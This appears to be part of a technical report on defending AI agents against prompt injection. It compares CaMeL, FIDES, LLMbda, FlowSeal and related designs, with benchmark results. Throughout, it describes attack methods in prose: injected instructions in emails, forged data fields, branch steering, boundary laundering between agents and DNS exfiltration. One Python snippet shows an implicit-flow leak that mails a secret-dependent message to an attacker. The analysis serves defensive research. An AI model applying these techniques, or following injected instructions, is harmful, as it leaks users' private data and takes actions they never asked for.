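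One of the paper's ten case studies is an email and calendar assistant much like the one in this report. Its choice of actions should rarely depend on what an email contains, so planning first would not limit it much in most uses. The plan does need some flexibility. For example, telling a user's regular collaborators about a holiday requires a loop, because the assistant doesn't know in advance who they are or how many messages to send.

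The contents of the messages remain exposed. If the user replies to an attacker's email, an instruction hidden in that email could make the assistant encode private information in the reply using invisible characters, so even a user who reads every draft carefully could approve it.

### One request through CaMeL

CaMeL is the best-known code-then-execute system. Researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich introduced it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), partly to fix a flaw they had found in the dual-model pattern. *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) retells their example. A user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The planner never reads the notes, so the quarantined model has to extract the address. An attacker who has edited the notes can make that model return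 a different address. The plan then runs as written and sends the document to the attacker.

CaMeL's answer is to record where every value came from. Suppose the user of the email assistant writes, "Send Priya's phone number to the address in the caterer's last email." The planner might produce this program:

```
email   = latest_email(sender="caterer")
address = ask_quarantined("Find the contact address", email,
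                          output=EmailAddress)
priya   = staff_record("Priya")
send_mail(to=address,
          subject="Contact for Thursday",
          body="Please call Priya on " + priya.phone)
```

The language is a restricted form of Python, which most models write well. A special interpreter runs the program line by line:

1. The planner finishes the program before the harness has fetched any email, so it works only from the user's words and the descriptions of the tools.
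2. The interpreter fetches the email and records that it came from an outside sender.
3. The quarantined model reads the email and must return something in the form of an email address. The interpreter records that `address` came from `email` and is therefore untrusted too.
4. The interpreter looks up Priya and records that her phone number came from the staff records, along with who may read it.
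5. Before it sends anything, the interpreter checks the company's policy for the mail tool. Suppose the policy allows a message only if the recipient is a known contact or the user supplied the address. This address came from a stranger's email and is not on the list, so the interpreter stops and asks the user.

If the email contains a hidden request for the whole staff directory, the request has no effect, because the program has only one lookup, for Priya, and the email can't add another. If the hidden text supplies an attacker's address, the quarantined model may well return it. The policy check at step 5 is then the only protection left, and the user still has to notice that the address is wrong.

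CaMeL's records of origin and permitted readers are called capabilities. Willison points out that the quarantined model does easier work than the planner, so it could be a small model on the user's own computer. The company that hosts the planner would then never receive the user's emails.

### Attacks stopped and tasks lost

*Indirect Prompt Injections* (Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues, 2025) compares CaMeL's published AgentDojo results using GPT-4o with its own run of the same model without a defence.

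| | No defence | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| Successful attacks | 57.7% | 0% |
| Tasks completed, no attack | 83.0% | 53.6% |
| Tasks completed under attack | 50.0% | 54.5% |

CaMeL's task completion rate was about 29 percentage points lower than the undefended agent's when there was no attack, and about the same under attack. It also used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens.

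Bhagwatkar and colleagues propose a much simpler defence, in which a model rewrites each tool result to remove suspicious instructions. It also stopped every attack on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, and it completed 74.1% of tasks, but they take this as a sign that the benchmark's attacks are too weak. A rewriting model can make mistakes, and the adaptive attacks by Nasr and colleagues defeated other defences that had reported attack success rates close to zero. CaMeL's protection against added actions follows from its design, so it also covers attacks that nobody has written yet, if the interpreter works correctly.

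Results from later tests of CaMeL vary widely. *SecureClaw* (2026), which introduces a rival system of the same name, ran an adapted version of CaMeL's released code on all of AgentDojo. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. Four attacks succeeded against SecureClaw, which completed 59 tasks.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) provides the most informative comparison for current models. It measures only the effect of planning first, with CaMeL's policies switched off. It uses two benchmarks in which a lead agent delegates work to specialised ones: AssetOpsBench, which has tasks about industrial equipment, and MultiAgentDojo, an adaptation of AgentDojo made for the paper. The table gives the share of tasks completed when there is no attack, first without CaMeL and then with CaMeL on every agent.

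| Model | AssetOpsBench | MultiAgentDojo |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 88.4% → 67.0% | 91.1% → 84.4% |
| GPT-5.5 | 87.5% → 82.1% | 86.6% → 73.2% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.2% → 64.3% | 78.4% → 38.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.9% → 55.4% | 76.3% → 42.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 64.3% → 20.5% | 27.8% → 13.4% |

Stronger models generally lost less, but Fable 5 still lost 21 points on AssetOpsBench. Fable 5's MultiAgentDojo figures cover only 45 of the 97 tasks because it refused the rest, which were harmless. Peters-Gill and colleagues suspect that the model associated the benchmark with attacks.

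The security benefit also depended on the model. Without CaMeL, attacks on MultiAgentDojo succeeded 36.1% of the time against GPT-4.1, 1.5% against Fable 5 and never against GPT-5.5. With CaMeL, no model's rate exceeded 0.5%. For GPT-5.5, CaMeL reduced task completion by 13 percentage points with no measurable security benefit on this benchmark. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that stronger, adaptive attacks might still succeed. A company that already uses a resistant model would therefore be accepting fewer completed tasks in exchange for protection against attacks that a fixed benchmark does not contain.

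Enforcing security policies can reduce task completion more than planning does. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL three times on each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*. With policies off, CaMeL completed 66.7% of runs with GPT-5.2 and 70.8% with MiMo-v2.5. With policies on, it completed 37.5% with each model. The margins of error are around 25 percentage points, but the drop was similar for both models.

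Garby and colleagues also worked out which attacks planning stops by itself. In 97 of the 144 pairings of a task with an attack, the attacker needed a step that the plan for the user's task would not contain. For example, an attacker can't steal money through a plan that only summarises recent transactions. The other 47 needed only steps that the plan might already include, so they test whether the policies work. Five attacks succeeded across the two models with policies off, and none succeeded with policies on in any run that finished.

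Two of those five should have been impossible. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely, so the planner wrote a program with a branch for every tool the file might request. Although the plan was fixed in advance, an attacker who controlled the file could still choose which tools the agent used.

### False values in a fixed plan

The earlier request was to check whether the caterer has confirmed for Thursday and, if so, to tell Priya. A planner can write the steps in advance, with a quarantined model answering yes or no and the assistant sending Priya one message if the answer is yes. Suppose someone impersonates the caterer and sends an email confirming a booking that doesn't exist. The quarantined model answers yes and the assistant wrongly tells Priya that lunch is confirmed, even though the email contained no instructions and the plan ran as written.

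Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) call this branch steering in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*. They adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a graphical interface, whose planner has to write a plan for screens it will never see. Nearly every such plan deals with cookie notices, so an attacker can predict that step. In one of their attacks, an advertisement contained a fake cookie notice. The model that reads the screen reported the fake notice's position, and the agent clicked through to the attacker's site.

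A policy helps little when the agent acts by clicking on a screen. An interpreter can check who will receive an email, but it can't tell from a click's coordinates whether the click will log in, delete a file or open a malicious page. Foerster and colleagues tried comparing the screenshot with the page's underlying code, and asking a second model to confirm what the first one reported. They also built attacks against each check's weakness. Both checks depend on detecting something wrong, so they reintroduce the error rates that separation was meant to avoid.

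False data can mislead ordinary agents too. The Hacker News' *New Agent Data Injection Attack Can Make AI Agents Misclick* (2026) describes attacks that forged small details, such as who wrote a comment, without changing the user's task.

A quarantined model can also leak its inputs. In an example from *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), the model is given an attacker's email and the user's private notes, and drafts a reply. The injection makes it copy the notes into the draft, which the plan then sends. Recording where data came from solves this case, because the draft is marked private if any of its inputs was private, and the harness can refuse to send it.

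Some cases can't be decided by origin alone. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay the bill in a file, and an attacker has replaced the file with a false bill. The user did want the agent to act on that file. Garby and colleagues report that this kind of attack also succeeded in CaMeL's original evaluation, where CaMeL's designers treated it as out of scope. A rule based on origin can either block every payment that depends on a file or let this one through. Doing better requires judging whether the bill is genuine, which is the same problem a classifier has with a plausible email about a new payroll provider.

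Separation also does not protect the user from what appears on the screen. Willison's 2023 proposal describes an attack in which the quarantined model encodes private text and tells the user to paste it into a website in exchange for a funny picture. The planner is also exposed if the user copies an attacker's text into the request, because the design trusts everything the user types.

### Tasks that depend on what the agent reads

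An agent can't plan an ordinary request like "Work through the action items in Priya's email" without reading the email. An agent with one model would read the list and choose its tools accordingly. A CaMeL planner could write a branch for every tool, but the email's author would again control which tools run. It could instead stop and show the list to the user.

In Peters-Gill and colleagues' tests, CaMeL failed most often for a related reason. The agent discovered only partway through a task that it needed a step its program didn't include. In other cases, an assisting agent couldn't find data for the requested machine or period and returned data for a similar one. The lead agent's program was already written by then, so it continued with the wrong data.

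A planner also needs the format of tool results in advance, because it never receives the results themselves. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add a full description of what every tool returns, as CaMeL had done. They consider this a modest, one-time job for each set of tools.

Longer plans can cover more possibilities. The plans that Foerster and colleagues' system wrote for the graphical interface averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about 5 and 4 on AgentDojo. Roughly half of each plan was fallbacks that a given run never used. With the strongest models, the system kept up to 57% of an ordinary agent's performance on OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer tasks. This shows that an agent can plan before seeing the screen, even when the screen changes, but the loss in performance would rule this approach out for many users.

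FIDES, a related system, hides tool outputs from its planner, which chooses one action at a time instead of writing the whole program at the start. But according to Foerster and colleagues, it has the same basic difficulty as CaMeL when the untrusted text itself specifies the steps.

Other designs let a little information through. In *Twin Agent* (2026), one agent explores the untrusted material and sends short hints to a second agent, which takes the actions. Developers can limit the length of the hints to balance security against usefulness. In tests that included AgentDojo and software repairs, this design kept much of the original agent's performance and greatly reduced successful attacks. It offers no formal guarantee of security, because the second agent still reads hints that an attacker may have influenced.

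### Separation between agents

A group of agents may be open to attack even if every agent in it uses CaMeL. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed this with three agents. The user asked a lead agent to send Julie a summary of some job applicants on Slack, a workplace chat service. A database agent fetched the records, one of which contained an instruction to email them to an outside address. Neither agent's planner saw the instruction. But the lead agent's program pasted the summary into its request to a third agent, which handled messaging. The third agent treated that request as its user's words, so its planner read the instruction and added the email to its program.

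Every attack that still succeeded against CaMeL in the tests used this route, called boundary laundering. The remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each request from one agent to another into an instruction that the receiving planner reads and a set of named values that it can use without seeing. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. No attack on MultiAgentDojo succeeded against this version. Its average task completion rate on AssetOpsBench was 3.2 points lower than that of separate CaMeL agents, and on MultiAgentDojo the rate with GPT-5.5 fell from 73.2% to 66.0%.

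The proof covers agents arranged in a hierarchy, where each takes requests from only one other agent. Peters-Gill and colleagues leave for later work the case where agents share a memory or write to each other freely.

### Policies and repeated questions

CaMeL's designers acknowledge that someone has to write and maintain its policies, and that users may tire of its questions. Willison is wary of any system that requires ordinary users to think about security policies, because he finds them hard himself after two decades working on application security.

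The email assistant's policy would interrupt the user for approval with every new contact, and the user would nearly always say yes. A user in the habit of approving may well approve the rare request they should refuse, as most developers did in Anthropic's approval experiment.

Better policies might require approval less often. Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori. Before reading anything, its planner decides which untrusted values a task may use. If the user asks it to pay the bill in a particular file, the plan can allow the payment details from that file in advance. Randori completed 75% of the banking runs with GPT-5.2, twice CaMeL's rate with policies on, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks across three models. Both successful attacks used a false payment file. But Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, which may account for part of the improvement.

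Garby and colleagues also found ways for secrets to escape CaMeL's tracking, so its guarantee is only as good as the interpreter's records.

### Use in products

In *Inside the lethal trifecta*, an article for the security company Sophos, McKerchar calls these designs promising but says that no mainstream harness had adopted them, naming Claude Code, Cursor, Hermes, GitHub Copilot Agent and Gemini CLI. McKerchar adds that no version of CaMeL was ready for production use. The article is undated but cites Google's April 2026 study of injections on the web, so it was written after that study and may not describe the situation in December.

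Research from the following months shows little sign of change. Peters-Gill and colleagues were still extending the existing research code in October 2026. Archestra, an agent platform company, has argued for the dual-model pattern on its blog, but that is weak evidence that customers are using it.

The test results help explain the slow uptake. A company that adopted CaMeL in 2026 would have had to maintain an unusual interpreter, describe every tool's output and write policies, and its agent would probably have completed fewer tasks. The strongest models were already resisting more attacks without any of this. McKerchar advises companies to limit the damage with controls outside the model, such as restricted network access and credentials that the agent never sees, rather than wait for these designs.

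McKerchar's statement concerns general-purpose harnesses, which a fixed plan would limit most. The simpler patterns need no special interpreter. A support chatbot that can only choose from a list of links, or a program that asks a model for a yes or no about each invoice, already prevents untrusted text from determining which action is taken. Its developers may be using the pattern without knowing the paper that named it.

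## Labelling data and controlling where it flows

CaMeL records where each value came from, so its interpreter can refuse to send a message to an address taken from a stranger's email. This technique, information flow control, is much older than language models. In 1976, Dorothy Denning described how a computer system could attach a security label to each piece of data, carry the labels along as programs combine the data, and let data move only where its label permits. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 71 works on recording what agents do, includes Denning's model among the field's foundations.

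### Two labels and a rule for combining them

An integrity label records who could have written a piece of data, and a confidentiality label records who may see it. In the simplest version, data is either trusted or untrusted, and either public or secret. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) also describes a finer version, in which each label is a set of people. The paper's system, Microsoft's FIDES, uses such labels in agents.

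When a program combines two pieces of data, x and y, the result gets the join of their labels, written ⊔. The join is the least restrictive label that respects both. For sets of people, it works like this:

writers(xy) = writers(x) ∪ writers(y)

readers(xy) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

When a system combines two pieces of data, the label on the result lists everyone who could have written either piece, because any of them could have influenced the result. It lists as readers only the people who have permission to see both pieces. Labels ordered in this way form what Denning called a lattice.

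The labels matter when the agent requests a sink. Costa and colleagues give two basic rules, which ordinary code checks just before the tool runs:

- The agent may take a consequential action only if the choice of tool and all the values passed to it are trusted.
- The agent may send data only to people who are permitted to read it.

The rule about readers doesn't stop an injection from steering the agent, but it limits what data the attacker can obtain. The rule about trust allows private data to leave if no untrusted text could have influenced the decision to send it, on the assumption that the user meant to send it. Enforcing both rules gives the strongest protection.

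### Three documents in one context

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes separating the influence of different inputs to a language model as an open research challenge. Labelling therefore uses the same cautious assumption as reach analysis, that everything in the context influenced the output:

label(output) = label(d₁) ⊔ label(d₂) ⊔ … ⊔ label(dₙ),

where d₁ to dₙ include the operator's instructions, the tool descriptions, the user's request and every tool result so far.

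Suppose the email assistant has three documents in its context when it writes to Priya about Thursday's lunch. The instructions and the request are trusted and public, so they don't change the result.

| Document | Integrity | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| The caterer's email | Untrusted | User, caterer |
| Priya's phone number, in a field that only HR can edit | Trusted | User, Priya, HR |
| The user's notes on the lunch, shared with Priya | Trusted | User, Priya |
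| **Whatever the model writes next** | **Untrusted** | **User** |

The message to Priya now fails both rules. It is untrusted because the caterer's email was in the context, and Priya isn't allowed to read it because she was not a recipient of that email. The harness would block the message even if it contained only "Lunch is confirmed", because the label depends on what the model could have used, not on what it wrote.

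### Label explosion

Labels combine through a join, so adding a document can make the context's label more restrictive but never less. If one document in ten is untrusted, the chance that a context is still trusted after 20 documents is 0.9²⁰, or about 12%. The set of permitted readers shrinks in the same way. After a few steps, nearly everything the agent produces is labelled both untrusted and secret, even if nobody has attacked it. This is known as label explosion or label creep, and longer context windows make it worse because they hold more documents.

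Costa and colleagues measured the effect by adding labels and rules to an ordinary GPT-4o agent on the AgentDojo benchmark. The agent's completion rate fell from 98.8% to 37.5% on banking tasks and from 93.3% to 20.0% on Slack tasks. It did not fall on travel tasks, where many tools were safe to use in an untrusted context as long as no private data leaked.

### Hiding data and making exceptions

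One remedy is to keep restrictive data out of the context, as the dual-model pattern does with its named variables. FIDES hides a value only if reading it would raise the context's label. For an incoming email, the planner might see the sender and date, which the mail system verifies, but only variable names for the subject and body. The rules can then also be more precise. For example, the harness can require a trusted recipient while allowing untrusted text in the message body.

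Unlike CaMeL, FIDES also lets its planner open a variable. According to *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026), the context then takes on the variable's label, which restricts what the agent can do afterwards.

Another remedy is to label a model's answer based only on the messages that influenced it. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and others that identifies those messages and generates the answer again from them alone. If the caterer's email had no effect on the answer, the answer does not carry the email's label. FIDES does not use this method, but its design would allow it.

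The remaining option is to allow exceptions. Declassification lets data reach people whom its label excludes, for example when HR approves the release of a phone number. Endorsement lets the system treat untrusted data as trusted, for example when a user confirms that an address is correct. Both are necessary in practice, and each makes the guarantee depend on somebody's judgement.

FIDES can base exceptions on how much information a value can carry. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit, a choice among n options carries at most log₂ n bits, and free text has no such limit. Suppose the user asks the assistant to add a calendar event if any of the last three emails requests a meeting:

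1. The planner fetches the emails and receives only variable names for their contents.
2. It asks a quarantined model whether any of them requests a meeting. The software forces the answer to be true or false.
3. The planner opens the answer. The company's policy accepts this untrusted value because one bit is too small to hold an instruction.
4. If the answer is true, the quarantined model extracts the date, time and participants into another variable.
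5. The planner passes that variable to the calendar tool without reading it.

An attacker who wrote one of the emails can create a false event but can't make the planner call a different tool. Even a one-bit answer can do harm if getting it wrong has serious consequences, as with the forged email confirming the caterer's booking.

### FIDES in tests

In Costa and colleagues' AgentDojo tests, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary GPT-4o agent. FIDES with its rules off reduced that number to 21 by hiding untrusted data in variables. Some attacks still succeeded because nothing prevented the planner from opening an untrusted variable and carrying on as before. Turning the rules on added checks at the sinks, and no attacks succeeded.

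The table shows the share of tasks completed when there was no attack.

| Setting | Ordinary agent | Ordinary agent with rules | FIDES with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

With GPT-4o, FIDES completed 50% of tasks on average, compared with 84% for an unprotected agent. Most companies would make this comparison, because an unprotected agent is what they already have. Costa and colleagues emphasise that FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks on average than an ordinary agent under the same rules, or 16 points more with OpenAI's o1 model.

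The loss depends partly on the kind of work. Costa and colleagues sorted the tasks by whether the right sequence of actions depends on what the agent reads. It does in only 5% of workspace tasks, but in more than 40% of tasks in banking and Slack. Many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which FIDES blocks by design. The workspace setting is closest to the email assistant, so the assistant might lose less than the average.

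The perfect security result is also partly due to the test's set-up. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it, so their labels already covered every attack in the test. A company has to decide which fields to trust without knowing where an attack will come from. The evaluation also left out the exceptions for small values, so it doesn't show how safe those are. The rules don't cover an attack that only changes what a text says, such as an email that makes a summary empty.

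### Forged details and the cost of strict tracking

Labels have to be precise because a single tool result often mixes trusted and untrusted data. For example, an inbox search returns the sender's address, which the mail system supplies, along with a body in which the sender can write anything. Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026) exploited this mixture in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, the research behind The Hacker News article on forged details mentioned earlier.

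In one example, the body of an attacker's email imitates the end of that email and the start of another that appears to come from Alice. The mail tool marks the attacker's punctuation as ordinary text, so a conventional program would find one email, but language models often find two. In tests of six models on JSON, a common format for structured data, between 31.3% and 43.3% of such forgeries succeeded. Imitation punctuation also worked, even with dollar signs in place of quotation marks.

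The forgery contains no instruction, so training a model to ignore instructions in data does little against it. On a version of AgentDojo, ordinary injections succeeded against an agent using GPT-5.2 0.2% of the time, while forged data succeeded 49.1%. Meta's Prompt Guard 2 classifier detected none of the 108 forgeries. CaMeL without its policies let 25.0% of them through, because the quarantined model extracted the forged values and the plan then used them.

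Choi and colleagues report both security and task completion for these defences:

| Defence | Forged-data attacks that succeeded | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 49.1% | 86.5% |
| Random tags added to field names | 28.7% | 83.3% |
| Progent, which restricts tool calls by policy | 22.2% | 81.4% |
| CaMeL with strict tracking | 0% | 36.5% |

Strict CaMeL was the only defence that stopped every attack, but the agent completed 58% fewer tasks as a result. Strict tracking covers decisions as well as data, so if an untrusted value determines which branch of a program runs, everything in that branch becomes untrusted too. Choi and colleagues also extended CaMeL's policies to cover the final answer to the user, which may explain some of the lost tasks.

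The random tags protect the boundary between fields with less overhead. The harness adds six unpredictable characters to each field name, so an attacker can't write a convincing fake "sender" field. The tags fail when the agent processes a whole list, for example to add up transactions, because it may include a fake item despite the wrong tag.

CaMeL's normal setting, which has policies but tracks data less thoroughly, let through 23.1% of attacks, almost as many as with no policies. Choi and colleagues traced this to a programming error. When the quarantined model extracted a value from a tool result, the software dropped the value's label, so the policy check treated an attacker's data as clean. They reported the error to CaMeL's developers.

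### Where the tracking stops

Garby and colleagues argue that errors like this one are typical, because a guarantee about information flow covers only the flows that the system tracks. They give two other gaps in CaMeL as examples.

Suppose a program should not reveal whether an account balance is above some threshold. CaMeL blocks a program that sends an email directly if the balance is high, because a secret determines whether the email goes out. But a longer program can get the same information past the check. In outline, it looks like this:

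```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_mail(to="attacker", body="rich")
```

If the balance is high, the program sets `tmp` to false, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. The next condition fails, so the program skips the line that would change `rich`. CaMeL updates a variable's label only on lines that actually run, so `rich` stays public and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email is sent. The attacker can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives. Computer scientists have known about this kind of leak since the 1970s.

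The other gap is outside CaMeL's interpreter. When a policy blocks a program, ordinary Python code around the interpreter may retry in a loop, and nothing tracks what the loop reveals. Whether an attempt was blocked can disclose one bit about a secret. A one-bit leak is acceptable in most systems, but repeated attempts can leak more. A four-digit PIN has 10,000 possible values, so 14 yes-or-no answers are enough to identify it.

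An attacker would first have to get CaMeL's planner to write such a program, which is hard because the planner never reads the attacker's text. The examples show weaknesses in the second layer of protection, not complete attacks.

FIDES has a comparable gap, which Costa and colleagues deliberately accept. It tracks data that moves directly into a message, but not what an observer could infer from the agent's choice of actions. If the agent contacts a recruiter only when a private file says that someone is leaving, the recruiter could infer the departure from being contacted. Costa and colleagues reject a stricter rule because it would in effect ban any publicly visible action after the agent had read private data. Garby and colleagues consider such compromises defensible, but object that a reviewer can't tell from a given run whether an exception let through a harmless value or caused a leak.

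An alternative is LLMbda, a small programming language for agents that labels every value, including the conversation with the model. A program can copy a conversation, use the copy to process untrusted text and then discard it, which gives the same isolation as the dual-model pattern without building that pattern into the harness. The interpreter stops the program if a secret determines whether a branch runs and that branch would add a message to a public conversation. Exceptions require an explicit `endorse` command, so a reviewer can find them all with a search. An exception for integrity leaves the confidentiality guarantee intact.

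Garby and colleagues wrote their agent, Randori, in a language called LLMbda. Their computer-checked proof shows that secret or untrusted inputs can't influence results whose labels exclude them. The proof covers every program in the language, including those a model writes during a run, and applies to the same interpreter that runs the agent. An observer may still learn something from whether a program finishes.

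Such a proof cannot establish that the labels are right. If a company marks a field as trusted when outsiders can edit it, the interpreter will enforce the wrong rule even when it works correctly. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* therefore counts the labels, and the software that carries and checks them, among the parts of a system that must work correctly for anything else to be secure.

### Private data that leaks without an injection

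Confidentiality labels also help when an outsider simply asks the agent for information. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, tested agents that hold private records, such as a man's mental health diagnosis that his ex-wife wants to obtain. The strongest existing defence they examined in detail was a prompt that told the agent to verify who was asking, request the man's consent and wait for his answer. It worked well against direct requests, but the agent had to recognise a request before it would follow the procedure. Three new attacks avoided looking like requests:

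- The attacker shares a document and asks the agent to fill in its section.
- The attacker lists true and false records and asks the agent to delete the errors. Whatever the agent leaves in place must be true.
- The attacker sends an email asking the agent to reply only "completed", while a separate shared page asks for the details.

The FlowSeal defence labels records by owner, using information such as email senders and document permissions. Code outside the model intercepts every attempt to write or share something. If the agent has read a protected record and the recipient is unknown, a second model must judge the proposed text "safe" or "blocked". This model receives only that text and the protected records, not the attacker's conversation.

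| Attack | Leaked with the consent prompt | Leaked with FlowSeal |
|---|---|---|
| Shared document | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Deleting errors | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Two channels | 43.8% | 2.2% |

The rates are shares of the sensitive items. In a smaller test with real Gmail and Notion accounts, the leak rate from the deletion attack was zero with FlowSeal and 34.7% with another model-based check. FlowSeal completed 72.4% of harmless requests, compared with 75.9% for the best of the other defences and 44.7% for the consent prompt. It added about two cents to the cost of each run and made runs 37% slower.

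The small loss of usefulness applies only to requests that need no private data. When the owner was willing to consent, FlowSeal's agent shared the records in 32.7% of cases, while agents using four other defences shared them in 61% to 86%. FlowSeal's agent also asked for consent less often.

Shim and colleagues also tested the system without the second model. When the code blocked every message to an unknown recipient after the agent had read a protected record, leaks stayed low at 1.3%, but the agent completed none of the harmless requests, which is another case of label explosion. When the code let those messages through, leaks rose to 24.9%. The fixed rules ensure that a check happens, but the agent is useful only because the second model decides which messages to exempt, and that model can miss a paraphrase. The tests also excluded prompt injection, so they don't show how the model would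 handle a message written to mislead it.

### Auditing a run afterwards

FIDES, CaMeL, LLMbda and FlowSeal can all stop an action before it happens. Cai and colleagues' NeuroTaint only audits the log of a finished run. A company could use it to find which email led to a leak, but by then the data would be gone. Because it runs afterwards, it can use slower and less certain methods, and a false alarm doesn't interrupt anyone's work.

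NeuroTaint stores labels alongside an agent's saved notes, so if the agent loads a planted note months later, the label comes back with it. NeuroTaint first looks for wording shared with the source and for a unique code that it added to the source earlier, then compares meanings. If it finds no trace of the source, it tests whether the agent would have acted without it. A language model predicts the outcome of the run without the source, which takes less compute than having the agent carry it out.

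NeuroTaint outscored FIDES on a set of 400 scenarios covering 20 agent frameworks. Half of the scenarios contain a real flow from source to sink. FIDES missed 92 of these 200 flows and raised 106 false alarms, mostly because it treats a possible path as evidence that data moved along it.

Two details make the gap less impressive. In four of the frameworks, FIDES flagged nothing, which looks more like a problem with the integration than a limit of the method. Those four account for 40 of its 92 misses, and excluding them would raise its F1 score from 0.522 to about 0.58. The two systems also performed almost identically on two established benchmarks, with F1 scores of 0.994 and 0.993 on the basic version of InjecAgent and 0.760 each on part of ToolEmu. Those benchmarks test whether an action was unsafe, not whether a particular source caused it, so NeuroTaint's advantage is in explaining incidents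 more than in detecting them.

An audit can also reduce what a stronger model has to review. Claude Opus 4.6 checked the 203 flows that NeuroTaint had flagged and dismissed all 16 false alarms, but also wrongly dismissed 8 real flows. NeuroTaint itself added an average of a quarter of a second per run.

All of this depends on a complete and unaltered log. Wang and colleagues found that few of the systems they surveyed had any reported protection against changes to their records. If an agent has permission to edit its own log files, an attacker who steers it could make it delete the evidence before anyone looks.

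## Limits enforced outside the model

Logs, labels and policies are reliable only if the agent can't edit them, so developers enforce the labels and policies in software that the model can't change. These limits still restrict the agent when a malicious email has completely deceived the model.

### The model as an untrusted component

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that designers should treat the model as untrusted, much as an operating system treats the programs it runs. An operating system has to cope with whatever a hostile program requests, and the software around a model should do the same with the model's requests. If that software blocks a forbidden action before it happens, there is no security violation, whether the request resulted from an attacker's email, an ordinary mistake or a goal that the developers never intended.

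The trusted computing base is the set of parts that must work correctly for these limits to be enforced. It includes the operating system, the sandbox, the policy and the reference monitor, which checks every requested action against the policy. The paper recommends keeping these parts small, because any of them could contain a flaw. The model, most tools and anything the tools return are not part of the trusted computing base.

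The five principles the paper used to classify eleven real attacks describe what this arrangement requires. Least privilege limits the policy to what the task needs, complete mediation and tamper resistance keep the agent from bypassing or changing the monitor, and secure information flow governs data the agent has already obtained. The fifth principle, the human weak link, includes users who click "allow", administrators who can write loose policies, and developers who can introduce bugs into the monitor.

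*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025), an earlier paper by many of the same researchers, explains why a language model makes a poor monitor. A model that denies 99% of unauthorised requests still lets 1% through, and an attacker can search for those. If its misses were independent, an attacker would have an even chance of at least one success within 69 attempts. A fixed rule can also be wrong, but an engineer can read it and correct it.

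### Permissions for one task

An agent's permission needs change with every request, whereas a phone app does a fixed set of things, so its developer can list the permissions it needs. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a user who tells a browser agent to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site for managing code. The agent needs only to open that issue and write in its comment box, and nothing else on the site. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent no longer needs to write. But its context now contains text that a stranger may have written, so the software has to revise the permissions without relying on that text.

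For the email assistant, the request to check the caterer's confirmation and tell Priya would need very little:

| Tool | Usual permission | Permission for this request |
|---|---|---|
| Inbox search | All messages | Messages from the caterer |
| Staff records | All employees | Priya's address |
| Web fetch | Any address | None |
| Mail tool | Any recipient | Priya |

With these limits, an instruction hidden in the caterer's email can't make the assistant look up another employee or write to an outsider. It can still make the assistant send Priya a false confirmation or a phishing link, because the task requires sending her a message.

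Giving the agent only the records its user may see is a less precise limit, but it needs no new policy for each request. In 2026 guidance reported in Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control*, Gee Rittenhouse of Amazon Web Services (AWS) and Eric Johnson of the SANS Institute, a security training organisation, advise companies to apply the user's existing permissions when the software retrieves records, before any results reach the context window. Instructing the model to withhold certain records is no substitute, because someone can prompt the model to ignore the instruction.

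If ordinary employees can't open their colleagues' home addresses in the personnel system, this filter prevents their assistants from leaking those addresses. It doesn't protect anything the user is allowed to see, so an HR manager's assistant could still leak every address in the company.

The filter also depends on knowing who is using the agent. NVIDIA's red team, which attacks systems to find their weaknesses, assessed a range of agents over six months. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* reports four recurring failures:

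- The agent did not restrict who could use it.
- Its tools let an attacker run arbitrary code.
- Nothing limited its outbound network connections.
- It had access to passwords and other secrets in plain text.

Missing access control was the most common weakness found in testing. Several agents held one employee's credentials but answered anyone on the internal network, so a colleague could act with that employee's permissions. NVIDIA recommends restricting each agent to named users and matching its permissions to those of the person making the request. In the tests, agents that ignored unauthorised users were much harder to attack.

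### Every route to the outside

The attack on Claude Code described earlier shows how a check can run and still fail. A connection test that needed no approval triggered a DNS lookup, which carried the secret keys out. NIST's *CVE-2025-55284 Detail* attributes the flaw to an overly broad list of safe commands in versions before 1.0.4.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* classifies this as a failure of least privilege and information flow rather than complete mediation. That is fair, because Claude Code did check the command against its list. But the list contained command names, and the leak came from a side effect of one of those commands. A monitor can therefore check every command and still miss a way for data to leave the computer. A rule at the network boundary could have blocked the lookup, whichever command caused it, if the rule covered lookups as well as ordinary connections.

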